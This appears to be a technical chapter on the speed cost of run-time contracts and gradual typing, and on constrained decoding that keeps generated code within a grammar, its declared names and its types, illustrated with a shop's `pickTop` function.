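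The wrapper in `guard` adds a function call each time the callback `score` is used, and it makes two checks per call, one on the item and one on the returned score. Sorting 1,000 products takes about 10,000 comparisons, so a version of `pickTop` that calls `score` twice in each comparison, like the sorts shown earlier, calls the wrapper about 20,000 times. A version that scores each product once and then sorts by the stored scores calls it 1,000 times.

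Suppose the generated code passes score to a helper in the shop's module, which passes it back, and each crossing adds a wrapper. After five crossings, every call to score goes through five wrappers that all make the same two checks.

| How pickTop uses score | Calls to score | Checks with one wrapper | Checks with five wrappers |
|---|---|---|---|
| once per item | 1,000 | 2,000 | 10,000 |
| twice per comparison | 20,000 | 40,000 | 200,000 |

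The postcondition adds another 1,000 calls to score, whichever version the model writes. If score only reads a field, the wrapper probably takes longer than score itself. If score queries a database, nearly all the added time comes from the postcondition's 1,000 extra queries. guard can avoid repeating queries by recording each score while pickTop runs and querying only the items that pickTop never scored.

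The two checks in guard are also far from equal. Testing for a finite number takes one step, but items.includes(item) searches the list from the start and examines about 500 products on average. Over 20,000 calls, that makes about 10 million comparisons. A set finds a member in roughly constant time, so two changed lines remove nearly all of this work:

```js
const known = new Set(items);       // once, before pickTop runs
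if (!known.has(item)) blame(user, "score received a non-item");
```

This enforces the same condition as before. A programmer should look for such savings before giving up any checks.

### The 2016 study

For years, researchers on gradual typing reported little about speed, and some papers timed only fully typed and fully untyped programs. Takikawa, Feltey and colleagues (2016) also timed partially typed programs in *Is Sound Gradual Typing Dead?* They took 12 Racket programs with 2 to 16 modules, prepared a typed and an untyped version of each module, and ran every combination 30 times. A program with n modules has 2ⁿ combinations, so the largest had 65,536.

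One of the programs, suffixtree, finds the longest piece of text that two strings share. With all six modules typed, it ran about 30% faster than with none, because the compiler used the types to speed up arithmetic and field access. But adding types only to the `label` module made it 88 times slower than the untyped version. Adding types to a second module made it 104 times slower, and typing the next three made little difference. The program became fast again only when the last module had types.

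A partly typed program can be slower than both its fully typed and fully untyped versions because only the partly typed one has boundaries between its own modules. In suffixtree, one module defines the tree's data and two others work on that data constantly, so the program's busiest code crosses any boundary among them. Greenman and colleagues report that over 100 million values cross two of its boundaries. The compiler also loses some optimizations, because any value might be in a wrapper and it can no longer read fields directly.

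Four of the 12 programs had a combination more than 100 times slower than the untyped version. Three others were 20 to 90 times slower at worst, and the remaining five were never more than 5 times slower. On average, about a fifth of the checking time in the slowest combinations was wasted on confirming that yes-or-no functions return true or false, even though Racket had generated nearly all of these functions itself.

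Takikawa and colleagues concluded that sound gradual typing was dead, given the technology of the time. Bauman and colleagues (2017) replied in *Sound gradual typing only mostly dead*. They reran the benchmarks on Pycket, an experimental compiler for Racket that optimizes code while it runs, and found much less overhead. Racket's own contract system also became faster. Moy, Nguyễn and colleagues (2020) measured many of the same programs on Racket 7.7 in *Corpse Reviver*, with and without a new tool. The table gives the slowdown of the worst combination in each case.

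| Program | Racket 6.2 (2016) | Racket 7.7 | Racket 7.7 with Corpse Reviver |
|---|---|---|---|
| snake | 122× | 16× | 1.6× |
| tetris | 117× | 11× | 1.3× |
| sieve | 114× | 19× | 1.0× |
| suffixtree | 105× | 32× | 1.0× |
| synth | 86× | 74× | 1.4× |

The first two columns come from different machines and slightly different versions of the programs, so they show only roughly how much Racket improved. Both columns of Racket 7.7 results come from the same experiment.

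### Proving that a check cannot fail

Corpse Reviver uses symbolic execution to remove checks that can never fail. Symbolic execution runs code on unknown values and follows every path the code could take. If no path through the untyped module can break a contract, the compiler can leave that contract out. Most of the checks are unnecessary because untyped code is usually consistent with the types, even though nobody has written them down.

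In sieve, for example, an untyped module computes prime numbers using a typed library. To find the 6,666th prime, it creates and calls almost 45 million small functions, which Typed Racket has to wrap. The analysis proves that the module always supplies a natural number and a function that returns the right kind of data, so every wrapper is removed.

The tool analyzes each module separately and keeps any contract it can't prove. Its average analysis time ranged from 5 seconds for sieve to 6 minutes for the slowest program. Moy and colleagues tested only 12 of the 20 programs in the standard collection, because the other eight use object-oriented features that the tool does not support.

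For pickTop, a similar tool could prove that the generated code passes only products from items to score, and drop that check. If score reads its figures from a file, the tool would have to keep the check that the result is finite, because the file's contents are unknown until the program runs. Someone would also have to repeat the analysis whenever the model rewrote the function.

More recently, Ferreiro and colleagues applied the same idea to Ciao, a version of the logic programming language Prolog. In a 22,000-line documentation generator, their analysis proved 70% of the conditions in its contracts and found errors that had gone unnoticed for years. With their best method, 18 small classic programs ran 156 times faster, by geometric mean, than with everything checked. However, the number of conditions proved is a poor guide to speed. Leaving one more condition unproved made one program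 32 times slower.

### Merging wrappers

A compiler that can't remove a check can still stop its wrappers from piling up. In the program fsm, a value gained four wrappers on each pass through a loop, and Greenman and colleagues measured a worst-case slowdown of 235 times on Racket 6.4. The program zombie ran up to 300 times slower while replaying just 100 commands. On Racket 7.7, Moy and colleagues measured slowdowns of 2.8 times for fsm and 60 times for zombie. They attributed the smaller pile-up in zombie to improvements in the contract system.

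Romero, Isla and colleagues (2025), in *Compiling Gradual Types with Evidence*, describe a compiler called GrEv that merges casts by combining their types. It attaches to each value a type, called evidence, that records what the program has established about the value so far. A new cast combines its own type with this record, keeping the more precise information from each:

```text
Product → ?       and  ? → number   give  Product → number
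Product → number  and  itself       give  Product → number
Product → number  and  ? → string   give  an error
```

The second line reduces five identical casts on score to one wrapper, so the 200,000 checks in the earlier table fall to 40,000. In the third line, number and string have no values in common, so the program stops as soon as it combines the casts, even if nothing calls the function.

Grift, an older compiler, also merges casts, but it keeps a value in plain form until a cast makes its type less precise, which makes fully typed programs fast. GrEv stores all values more uniformly, whether typed or not. On Grift's version of sieve, partly typed programs ran 2 to 128 times slower than Racket with Grift and 5 to 9 times slower with GrEv. GrEv was faster than Grift on most mixtures of typed and untyped code, but slower on most fully typed programs. It was also slow in some cases, including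 a graphics program whose worst mixture ran about 60 times slower than Racket.

Merging works well for types because a compiler can calculate their combination. The conditions in guard are arbitrary code, so a contract system usually has to detect when one wrapper makes another redundant instead, as Racket does where it can.

### Checks built into the engine

A JavaScript engine gives each object a hidden shape, which lists the object's fields and where they are in memory. Before running optimized code, the engine checks that an object has the expected shape. Richards, Arteca and Turcotte (2017), in *The VM Already Knew That*, added contracts to the shapes, so that the same check also covers the contracts.

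SafeTypeScript is a variant of TypeScript that enforces types at run time. Its original version slowed one set of benchmarks by a factor of 22 on average when typed and untyped code mixed. A rebuilt version slowed fully typed programs by 7% on average and the slowest mixture of typed and untyped code by 45%. On the largest program, the TypeScript compiler, checking nearly doubled memory use.

The method would let pickTop check a product's fields with little run-time overhead. It would help less with score, because Richards and colleagues had to fall back on explicit checks for the values that functions return. Their system also runs on a research engine, so TypeScript programmers can't simply switch it on.

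Nominal type systems make checks simpler. With concrete types, a program can check a list of 1,000 products by reading one tag instead of examining every product. Romero and colleagues say that Muehlboeck and Tate's nominal design allows substantially more efficient run-time representations.

### Choosing which annotations to keep

Having a tool infer types and add as many annotations as possible can increase the number of run-time checks, even though fully typed programs have no internal boundaries. Suppose a program passes a value from one untyped library function to another through a variable. Without an annotation on the variable, the program needs no check. If the tool correctly annotates the variable as an integer, the program has to cast the value when storing it in the variable and again when passing it to the second function.

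Li, Dai and colleagues (2026) built TypePycker, a tool that selects which inferred annotations to keep in Reticulated Python. It traces data flow backwards from each variable and keeps the inferred annotation only if the nearest sources already have known types. It never removes annotations that a programmer wrote.

TypePycker left out some of the inferred annotations in 41 of the 50 test programs. Of these, 32 ran faster than with every inferred annotation, six ran at about the same speed, and three ran slower, one of them because dropping an annotation moved a check from before a loop to inside it. Ten programs ran slower with every annotation than with none, but fastest with TypePycker's selection. TypePycker usually finished in under a second, whereas an older tool that compares all possible selections took over 2,000 seconds in the worst case.

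### Measuring a boundary before deployment

Most of these remedies require a particular language or compiler. A programmer who runs guard in ordinary JavaScript has to find the expensive checks and reduce them by hand, and can start with these steps:

1. Set a limit before measuring. According to Moy and colleagues, the payments company Stripe allows its Ruby type checker, Sorbet, to slow programs by only 7% before it alerts developers. Other programs can tolerate much more.
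2. Collect realistic calls and add larger ones, for example with 100, 1,000 and 10,000 products. The original guard takes over 100 times longer to check the callback's arguments when the list grows tenfold, which a test with three products would never reveal.
3. Time the whole operation with the plain function and with the guarded one. Let the engine warm up first, then alternate between the two and repeat each at least ten times. A check that doubles the time of pickTop may be unnoticeable if pickTop takes 1% of the time needed to build a page.
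4. If the result exceeds the limit, count the calls through each wrapper and use a profiler to find the slowest condition. In one mixture of suffixtree, the contract on a single function that reads a field took about 70% of the running time.
5. Repeat the measurement whenever the model rewrites the function. A new version may call score 20 times as often and still pass every test of its results.

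In a language with deep types, each choice of which modules to type needs its own measurement. Timing every choice soon becomes impractical, but Greenman and colleagues found that random samples give a good approximation. For a program with 13 modules, which has 8,192 possible choices, Moy and colleagues timed 1,300 chosen at random.

### Move the boundary or weaken the check

When a check is too slow, the quickest response is to weaken it, for example by switching from deep to shallow types. This helps if a few large values cross the boundary between typed and untyped code and the program uses only small parts of them. But shallow checks run throughout typed code, so they take more time as programmers add types. *Optimizing and Evaluating Transient Gradual Typing* (2019) found that programs in Reticulated Python slowed steadily as they gained types and were slowest when most fully typed.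 With deep types, by contrast, adding the last few annotations may remove the slow boundary.

Moving the boundary is better when the existing boundary separates pieces of code that constantly exchange values. Greenman and colleagues give the example of a short untyped script that used a typed library for storing data in trees. The script took about 12 seconds to run. Changing its first line to make it typed removed the boundary and cut the time to less than a millisecond.

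The generated code should stay behind a boundary, but the shop can choose where that boundary lies. Instead of passing score to the model's function, it can calculate the scores itself and ask the model for a function that works only on numbers:

```js
const scores = items.map(item => score(item));  // the shop's code
const chosen = pickPositions([...scores], k);   // the generated code
return chosen.map(i => items[i]);               // the shop's code
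```

The function `pickPositions` returns the positions of the k highest scores. The shop checks once that each of the 1,000 scores is finite. After the call, it checks that `chosen` contains k different valid positions and that no omitted score is higher than a chosen one. No callback crosses the boundary, so there are no wrappers to call or accumulate. The generated code never receives a product, so it can't change one. The postcondition uses the same scores as the function did, even if a sale comes in meanwhile.

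Sometimes the boundary can't move, for instance because other programs depend on pickTop's signature. If the postcondition is still too slow after the simpler repairs, the shop can run its slowest clause on a random one in every hundred calls and the other checks on every call. A reversed sort would still show up quickly on a busy site, but a fault that affects only a few unusual lists could go unnoticed for a long time.

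## Keep unfinished code within the grammar and the names in scope

A contract can catch a fault in pickTop only when the shop runs the function, and the contract's tests take time on every call. Constrained decoding excludes tokens that would break a formal rule while the model is writing. This prevents some faulty programs, and the finished program needs no extra checks for that rule. The simplest rules cover grammar, such as closing every bracket, and names, such as using only declared variables.

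### The start of a run and the start of a text

Contracts and masks both apply to something unfinished, since guard tests a call to score partway through a run, and a mask excludes a token while the program is only partly written.

*Enforceable Security Policies* (Schneider, 2000) proves that a monitor that watches a program's steps and stops the program before a forbidden one can enforce only safety properties. One of the paper's example policies forbids a program to send a message after it has read a file. The monitor can record past steps but has no information about later ones, so it must stop a run as soon as it becomes unacceptable. Even if the next steps would put things right, the program might end before reaching them.

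Basin and colleagues (2012) restate one of his conditions as a rule that an acceptable run never starts with anything bad. Program text breaks this rule because even a valid program is invalid if cut off at nearly any character. For example, `return ranked.slice(0, k` is not a valid statement, but adding `);` makes it one. Like the trace contract for Racket's drawing library, a mask must therefore accept anything unfinished that could still become valid. It can test for this because the rules of the language determine which continuations are possible, whereas there is no general way to work out what a running program will do next.

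| | Contract at run time | Mask during generation |
|---|---|---|
| Examines | the start of one run | the start of a program's text |
| Uses | actual values | the language's rules and the names so far |
| Tests whether | something has gone wrong | the text can still become valid |
| Covers | the calls that happen | every run of the finished program |
| After a fault | stops with an error and a blame label | excludes the token without a message |

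A mask can therefore keep pickTop from using an undeclared variable, even in a branch that no test reaches. But it can't ensure that score returns a finite number, because no scores exist until the code runs.

### The prefix language and the decoding loop

Mündler and colleagues define a mask's task using a prefix language. If L is the set of complete, valid programs, its prefix language Lᵖ contains every text that some further text can turn into a member of L:

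```text
Lᵖ = { s | s followed by s′ is in L, for some s′ }
```

The added text s′ may be empty, so every complete program is in Lᵖ too. Constrained decoding adds an inner loop to ordinary generation, which keeps the text in Lᵖ:

```text
text = the start of the program, which may be empty
repeat
    p = the model's probabilities for the next token
    repeat
        t = a token drawn according to p
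        if t is the end marker:  accept it if text is in L
        otherwise:               accept it if text + t is in Lᵖ
        if not accepted:         set p[t] to 0 and rescale p
    until t is accepted
    if t is the end marker, return text
    text = text + t
```

The inner loop draws again from the same probabilities, leaving out the rejected tokens, so it doesn't rerun the model. It usually needs only a few draws. It always finds an acceptable token, because an unfinished text in Lᵖ has at least one possible next character and the vocabulary includes all common characters as single tokens. Many systems compute the whole mask first, which gives each token the same probability as testing tokens one at a time.

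The text starts in Lᵖ, every accepted token keeps it there, and the loop returns it only once it is in L. Any program the loop returns is therefore valid, however poorly the model has learned the rules.

The hard part is testing whether a text is in Lᵖ. An ordinary compiler tests only for L, so someone has to write a second checker that follows the same rules. Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues report that Rust's compiler-related code alone exceeds 600,000 lines. They note that existing constrained decoders therefore enforce only the grammar or part of the type rules.

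### Why brackets are easier than names

A context-free grammar is a set of rules for building larger pieces of text from smaller ones. One rule might define a call as an expression followed by an opening bracket, a list of arguments and a closing bracket. A parser, which reads text according to these rules, keeps a stack of the pieces it has started but not finished. After `ranked.slice(0, k`, the piece on top is the list of arguments. The next character can extend `k`, start another argument or close the bracket, but it can't be a semicolon.

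A typical grammar requires only that a name be a letter followed by more letters or digits. If `pickTop` stores its sorted list in `ranked`, the grammar still accepts `sorted.slice(0, k)`, even if `sorted` is undefined. *ChopChop* (2025), which describes a system for stricter constraints, gives an extreme example in which CodeLlama-7B, constrained only by a grammar, wrote natural language that happened to parse as a program but contained undefined variables.

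A better context-free grammar would not help, because no context-free grammar accepts exactly the programs that declare every name before using it. Zhang, Xu and colleagues (2026) show this in *Constrained LLM Generation over a Refinement Order of Grammar Fragments*, using an argument similar to Robert Floyd's 1962 proof about ALGOL 60.

1. Keep only the programs of the form `let w; w′;`, where w and w′ stand for names that consist of the letters a and b. A regular expression can describe this form, and selecting texts with a regular expression always turns one context-free language into another.
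2. These programs declare only w, so w′ must be the same name. The remaining programs are `let a; a;`, `let ab; ab;` and so on.
3. Delete the fixed parts and put a marker between the names, which leaves `a#a`, `ab#ab` and so on. This step also preserves context-freeness.

The result is the copy language, in which the same word appears on both sides of the marker. By a standard theorem, no context-free grammar describes this language, so the supposed grammar cannot exist.

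The parser's stack gives some intuition for this, because it returns its contents in reverse order. That suits brackets, since the last one opened is the first to close. After storing `ab`, the stack can easily match `ba`, but a repeated name needs the letters in their original order, `ab`.

### Read the names into the grammar

The names in scope at a point in a program are those that code at that point may use. Compilers handle names separately from grammar, looking up each one in a type environment, written Γ, which records the names in scope and their types.

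Synchromesh, which Gabriel Poesia and others presented in 2022, used such information during generation. It worked out from the text so far which continuations a language allowed, and restricted the model's tokens to those. Monitor-guided decoding, which Lakshya Agrawal and others published in 2023, consulted a static analyzer at chosen points, such as after the dot in `product.`, and allowed only names of a suitable type. The analyzer examined the whole repository.

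Zhang and colleagues instead change the grammar itself as the program grows, and call the result a decode-time grammar. Their system works through a program as a series of gaps:

1. At a gap where a name belongs, it looks up the suitable names in Γ.
2. It puts these names into the grammar in place of the rule that allows any identifier.
3. XGrammar, an existing engine for enforcing grammars, turns the new grammar into masks, and the model fills the gap.
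4. If the model has declared a new name, the system adds it to Γ before the next gap. When a block of code ends, the names local to that block drop out.

Mündler and colleagues also take names from Γ, in a checker that searches for ways to reach the required type as well.

Zhang and colleagues tested mostly small, specialized languages, but the same steps work for a gap in pickTop. Suppose the model has written the first two lines below and has to choose the name at the underscore:

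```ts
function pickTop<T>(items: T[], k: number, score: (item: T) => number): T[] {
  const ranked = [...items].sort((a, b) => score(b) - score(a));
  return _.slice(0, k);
```

Γ contains items, k and score from the first line and ranked from the second. The names a and b were local to the function inside sort, so they have dropped out. Leaving aside pickTop itself and JavaScript's built-in names, the grammar for this line becomes:

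```text
line ::= "return " ("items" | "k" | "score" | "ranked") ".slice(0, k);"
```

If the model's most probable next token is "sorted", a name the program never declared, the mask excludes it. The mask allows the token "s", because score begins with it, but the next character must then be c. A stricter grammar could also filter the names by kind. Numbers and functions have no slice method, so only items and ranked would remain.

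Without the parentheses around the four names, XGrammar would parse the rule as a choice between `return items`, `k`, `score` and `ranked.slice(0, k);`. The first of these would return the whole list.

Zhang and colleagues proved that a program generated in this way cannot contain an undeclared name if the grammar treats every use of a name as a gap of this kind, every gap has at least one candidate, and every candidate is in Γ. The proof traces each name in the finished text back to its gap. Only a candidate could fill that gap, and the program had already declared every candidate by that point.

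The theorem also assumes that XGrammar enforces the grammar exactly. In tests, XGrammar accepted all 90 valid strings and rejected all 772 invalid ones. If Γ contains no suitable name, a declaration is missing, and the system can detect this before the model writes another token. The system can then fall back to allowing any identifier, but it loses the guarantee for that gap.

### Why a fixed set of grammars is not enough

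Zhang and colleagues proved that no finite set of grammars prepared in advance is enough to avoid building new ones during generation, even with a perfect rule for switching between them. They call a mask sound if it never offers an undeclared name, and non-blocking if it never excludes a continuation that uses only declared names.

Suppose there are 100 grammars, each offering a fixed set of names, and 101 unfinished programs. Each program has declared one variable, with a name no other program uses, and is about to use it. To be both sound and non-blocking, the mask must offer exactly the declared name, so each program needs a different set. At least two programs must share a grammar, and its set is wrong for at least one of them. The same argument works for any finite number of grammars, because a programming language has no practical limit on the number of possible names.

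If programs could use only 20 names, one grammar for each possible combination would be enough. That would already take over a million grammars.

### What a list of names can enforce

Zhang and colleagues use Γ to store each name along with its kind and, for matrices, its dimensions. They divide program properties into those that a mask can enforce from this record and those that need another method. The examples in the table apply their division to pickTop.

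| Property | Enforceable from Γ? | Example |
|---|---|---|
| The program has declared the name | yes | excludes sorted if only ranked exists |
| The name is of the right kind | yes | excludes k before .slice |
| The declaration comes in an earlier gap | yes | allows ranked only after its declaration |
| Sizes match, if they are fixed at declaration | yes | requires a list with one score per item |
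| The values are correct | no | would have to detect a reversed sort |
| The program terminates | no | would have to detect an endless loop |
| A changeable property holds | no | would have to track whether a list is still sorted |

The third property holds only from one gap to the next. If the whole call to sort were a single gap, the model would declare a and b and use them inside it, and the system could not update Γ in between. For the last three properties, Zhang and colleagues suggest a verifier, a monitor with its own memory, or a separately verified set of continuations.

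### Results for SQL and TileLang

In SQL, the standard language for database queries, Γ is the database's list of tables and columns. Zhang and colleagues tested Qwen3-0.6B, a deliberately small model, on 60 query-writing samples. A query counted as correct only if its result matched that of a reference query.

| Method | Correct | Invented columns | Tokens per query |
|---|---|---|---|
| Grammar that allows any name | 0% | 60 | 20.8 |
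| No constraint | 70.0% | 11 | 22.9 |
| No constraint, legal columns in the prompt | 93.3% | 4 | 17.2 |
| No constraint, up to four retries | 90.0% | 5 | 40.0 |
| Grammar with names from Γ | 100% | 0 | 6.6 |

The model did worse with a grammar that left names open than with no constraint, so the rise from 0% to 100% overstates the benefit. Listing the legal columns in the prompt gave most of the improvement without changing decoding, although the model still invented four columns. In the paper's example, the grammar also supplied much of the query, including the table name, so the model had fewer chances to make a mistake.

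On another set of simple queries, the system got 85% right when it allowed every column in the database and 100% when it allowed only the relevant table's columns. Both versions excluded invented names, but the first still let the model choose a real column from the wrong table.

TileLang is a language for programming graphics processors, and models have few examples of it to learn from. When the grammar allowed any name, none of the programs by four models compiled, even though the largest model had 120 billion parameters. When it allowed only names in scope (Γ), between 67% and 83% of the programs by the three smaller models compiled, and undeclared names caused none of the remaining failures.

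The much larger DeepSeek-V4-Flash also failed without a constraint. All eight of its first programs used forms from TVMScript, a related language, such as T.Buffer instead of TileLang's T.Tensor. With grammars for TileLang, it wrote 20 programs with no invented names. Nineteen computed the right numbers, and the other compiled but needed too much memory. A more capable model may have learned the related language better, which makes the wrong name more probable, but a mask excludes that name regardless of its probability.

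A mask is especially useful where mistakes produce no error message. In CMake, a tool for building software, a misspelled variable silently becomes an empty string. Zhang and colleagues found that 8 of 11 kinds of CMake error gave no message, so a model that relies on error messages to repair its code would get no help with them. JavaScript also gives no error when a field is misspelled, which is how the shop came to advertise "undefined".

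Building grammars during generation reduced throughput. The model produced 10.6–17.8% fewer tokens per second than with XGrammar and a fixed grammar, and 17.3% fewer on average than with no constraint (up to 29.9% fewer for the small model). A query may still finish sooner, because the masked SQL queries used less than a third as many tokens as the unconstrained ones.

### A scope check for MLIR

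*Cross-Dialect Generalization Without Retraining* (Rath, 2026) presents a similar decoder for MLIR, a format that machine-learning compilers use internally. The decoder keeps a table of the values defined so far. When the program uses a value, the mask allows only tokens that continue a name in the table, and when the program defines a value, the mask requires a new name.

Rath proved that every program this decoder completes passes the scope check, but in a test on ten prompts, the decoder produced text that parsed for only two and hit its token limit on the other eight. It was also about 44 times slower than the alternative. According to Rath, the decoder got stuck because the model could start a name with a token that could not be extended to any name in the table. A mask that tested exactly for the prefix language would have excluded that token. The proof covers only finished programs,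 so it does not rule out this failure.

All of Rath's main results come from a simpler method. Masks enforce the grammar and some type rules during generation, then a separate check accepts or rejects the whole program based on how it uses names. After a rejection, the model tries again, up to a fixed limit. Rath proved that this method accepts the same programs as the decoder that checks names token by token.

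On 200 tasks involving arithmetic and functions, 20.0% of the programs that the small model SmolLM2 wrote without constraints passed MLIR's own verifier. The masks raised this to 45.5%, and adding the scope check with its retries raised it to 52.0%. When Rath replaced the masks with a grammar check after each of a limited number of attempts, only 24.5% passed.

Valid programs were often still wrong. On linear algebra tasks, 80.0% of programs passed the verifier. In a separate test of 22 valid programs for such tasks, only eight computed the requested function through the requested interface. Thirteen declared different inputs or outputs.

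A programmer whose model runs on a service that does not accept custom masks can still check the finished text. For pickTop, the TypeScript compiler can check scope, and the programmer can ask for another version whenever the compiler reports an undeclared name.

### Package names

A generated pickTop might also rely on a library that does not exist. Models often recommend packages with invented names, and they tend to repeat the same names. An attacker can publish a malicious package under one of these names and wait for someone to install it.

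*PackMonitor* (Liu, Liu and colleagues, 2026) describes a mask for this problem. The mask uses a list of the 706,618 package names then on PyPI, the main repository of Python packages. It takes effect when the model writes "pip install" in a block of code. It then allows only tokens that continue a listed name, and lets the name end only when it is complete. This excludes google-protobuf, for example, a plausible name that is not on the list.

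The list does not depend on what the model has declared, so one precompiled structure is enough. Building it took 4.4 seconds, while loading a saved copy took less than a tenth of a second.

In tests of five models, invented names made up between 3.25% and 8.39% of recommended packages without the mask, and none with it. The mask increased average response times by 7% to 28%. Asking the models to check their own answers left some invented names in every case. An earlier project had fine-tuned two of the models to avoid invented packages. On a separate set of tasks, fine-tuning reduced DeepSeek-Coder's rate of invented packages from 16.14% to 2.66%, but the share of HumanEval tasks it solved fell from 72.6% to 45.7%. The mask did not change that share.

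With PyPI's list, PackMonitor can't block an invented name that an attacker has already registered, because that name is on the list too. A list of packages that the shop's programmers have approved would be safer, and PackMonitor can use a custom list. The version that Liu and colleagues tested covers only "pip install" commands, so a model could still put an invented name in a requirements file, which lists the packages a project needs.

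### Where the guarantee stops

A declared name can be the wrong one. In pickTop, items and ranked are both lists in scope at the gap, so the mask allows either. If the model fills the gap with items, the function returns the first k products, which is one of the five wrong versions in the mutation test. guard rejects that result whenever an omitted product has higher sales than a returned one. A mask can even contribute to such a mistake. In an example from *AdapTrack* (Li, Li and colleagues, 2025), it steers a model from a function that no longer exists to a real one that does something else.

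Γ must also match the program. If the system did not remove `a` and `b` when their function ended, the mask would allow `return a.slice(0, k)`, which uses an undeclared name. If Γ lacked JavaScript's built-in names, the model could not write `Math.max`, and if it lacked helper functions defined further down, the mask would block correct programs that call them. Rath measured errors of this kind and found that the scope check rejected 3 of 89 valid programs from one set because it read the code line by line and mishandled operations that continued on the next line.

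Generation can also run out of tokens in the middle of a program. The mask ensures that some valid ending exists, but not that the model reaches it within the limit. Schneider's monitors had to stop an unacceptable run at once for a similar reason, since the program might end before the run became acceptable. Zhang and colleagues point to a remedy that also tracks the remaining tokens and excludes any token after which the program could no longer finish within the limit. Without this remedy, the shop should discard any pickTop that stopped at the limit, even if the partial code looks correct.

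## Enforce types token by token

A grammar built from Γ can filter single names by type. But most expressions are longer than one name, and their type depends on code the model has not written yet, so a mask for types has to check expressions before they are finished.

### An argument that begins with the wrong type

The unfinished call to parseInt that Mündler and colleagues use as an example belongs to a function that should report whether a text is a whole number:

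```ts
function is_int(text: string): boolean {
  const num = Number(text);
  return !isNaN(num) && parseInt(num
```

An ordinary type checker would reject the call because num is a number and parseInt expects a string, although later text can still repair it. The checker cannot simply skip the last expression either, because some continuations are already beyond repair:

| Next text | Grammar only | Grammar and types | Reason |
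|---|---|---|---|
| `;` | excluded | excluded | the bracket is still open |
| `ber` | allowed | excluded | the program never declared "number" |
| `()` | allowed | excluded | a number is not a function |
| `, 10)` | allowed | excluded | the argument ends while it is still a number |
| `.toString()` | allowed | allowed | the argument becomes a string |

Without constraints, CodeLlama 34B wrote ", 10)", and the program did not compile. When the token mask enforced types, the model wrote ".toString()" and completed the function correctly.

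### Type inhabitation

Type inhabitation is the classic question in type theory of whether any expression has a given type. *Inhabitation in Simply-Typed Lambda-Calculus through a Lambda-Calculus for Proof Search* (2016) states it for the simply typed lambda calculus, a minimal language in which programs only define and apply functions. Given a type environment Γ and a type A, the question is whether any expression has type A in Γ.

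Suppose Γ contains product, of type Product, and score, of type Product → number. Then the type number is inhabited, because score(product) is a number. If Γ contains only score, no expression has type number, because there is nothing to pass to score and the minimal language has no literals such as 0.

For simple types, an algorithm can always find the answer, a result usually credited to Richard Statman (1979). But Kuśmierek notes in *The Inhabitation Problem for Rank Two Intersection Types* that the problem is PSPACE-complete. It is therefore as hard as any problem a computer can solve with a polynomial amount of memory, and no known algorithm solves every case in polynomial time.

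Richer types make inhabitation harder to decide. An expression has the intersection type A ∩ B if it has both type A and type B, and TypeScript has a similar construct, written A & B. No algorithm can decide inhabitation for intersection types in general. Kuśmierek proved that the problem is decidable for a restricted form, rank two, but EXPTIME-hard, so every algorithm for it takes more than polynomial time on some inputs. *Inhabitation for Non-idempotent Intersection Types* (2017) gives algorithms for systems in which A ∩ A is not the same type as A.

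In TypeScript, it is easy to tell whether a model can produce an expression of the required type if it has written nothing yet, because a literal such as 0 or "" will do. It is harder once the model has written part of an expression, since the rest must build on that part. Mündler and colleagues therefore check whether that part can still become an expression of the required type.

### An automaton without dead ends

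An automaton reads a text one character at a time, moving between states. Some are accepting states, which mark a complete, valid text. Many automata also have dead ends, states that lead to no accepting state. An automaton that compared types only at the end of a statement would read all of "parseInt(num, 10)" before getting stuck.

Mündler and colleagues built a prefix automaton, which has no dead ends:

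```text
for every text s, and every state q that the automaton can reach by reading s,
some further text s′ leads from q to an accepting state
```

With this property, a text belongs to the prefix language, meaning it has a valid completion, exactly when the automaton is in at least one state after reading it. The decoding loop can therefore feed each proposed token to the automaton, character by character, and reject the token if no state remains.

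The automaton can be in several states at once because unfinished text is ambiguous. If both score and scores are in scope, the text "score" may be a complete name or the start of a longer one. Each state records the piece of syntax in progress, the current Γ, and the type the context requires. Because the number of possible states is unlimited, the automaton can enforce rules that no context-free grammar can express.

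Mündler and colleagues built the automaton from smaller ones that match names, literals and fixed words. They combined these by joining them in sequence, offering them as alternatives, or repeating them, and proved that these operations introduce no dead ends as long as the second part of a sequence can match some text.

The same method covers whole statements, with Γ updated as the program grows. Inside a function, the automaton also tracks whether every path returns a value of the declared type. DeepSeek Coder 33B wrote a function to find the largest divisor of n, with its only return statement inside a loop. If n is negative, the loop never runs and the function would return undefined. The mask did not allow the function to end after the loop, so the model added "return 1;" there.

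### The search for the required type

To decide whether an unfinished expression can reach a required type, the automaton first works out its derivable types. These are the types it could have if the model finished the current piece and added nothing more. Suppose a version of pickTop for plain numbers has these names in scope:

```text
items: number[]    k: number    score: (item: number) => number    scores: number[]
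```

| Fragment | Derivable types |
|---|---|
| `k` | number |
| `score` | (item: number) => number, or number[] if the name becomes scores |
| `score(` | number |
| `items.le` | number, because only length begins this way |

If none of these is the required type, the automaton searches for operations that lead to it. The search uses a directed graph whose nodes are types and whose edges are operations. Adding a number to a `number` leads back to `number`. Accessing `toString` on a `number` leads to `() => string`, the type of a function that takes no arguments and returns a string, and calling that function leads to `string`.

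```text
reachable(T, goal):
    if T is the goal, return yes
    if the search has visited T before, return no
    mark T as visited
    for each operation that leads from T to some type S:
        if S is too complex, skip it
        if reachable(S, goal), return yes
    return no
```

For "parseInt(num", the search starts at the type number and looks for a way to reach string. Addition leads back to number, which the search has already visited. Accessing toString gives a function that returns a string, and calling that function gives a string. The mask therefore allows a dot after num. After the dot, it allows only letters that spell number members that can still lead to a string, so it would exclude ".sort".

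The search considers only types, but every path it finds can be written as code, because a literal of the right type is always available when an operation needs an argument. A "yes" therefore guarantees that a valid continuation exists.

### Why some valid programs are refused

The map has infinitely many points because every value in TypeScript has a member called `valueOf`, a function that returns the value itself. From `number`, it leads to `() => number`, whose own `valueOf` leads to `() => () => number`, and so on. Without a limit, a search for an unreachable type would never end.

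Mündler and colleagues limit the search by counting how many function layers surround a type's final result. The search skips a type with more layers than both the current type and the goal, unless that type contains a basic type the search has not yet reached. When searching from `number` to `string`, it skips `=> number`, a function that returns a number, because that type contains no new basic type, but it follows `=> string`.

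Because of the limit, the search can miss a valid path, and the mask then excludes correct code. The constraint is still sound, because it allows only valid programs, but it is incomplete, because it doesn't allow all of them. Mündler and colleagues argue that the search misses only complex types that rarely occur in practice, though they have no proof.

The tool's limited coverage of TypeScript probably excludes more. It has 11,249 lines of Python, while the official compiler has over 427,000 lines. It does not support classes, type declarations, generic function declarations or most imports, so it could not generate pickTop with the type variable T, or with a Product type that the shop had declared. It also requires a function to be declared before its first use, so it would reject a call to the helper byScore if the definition were to come later.

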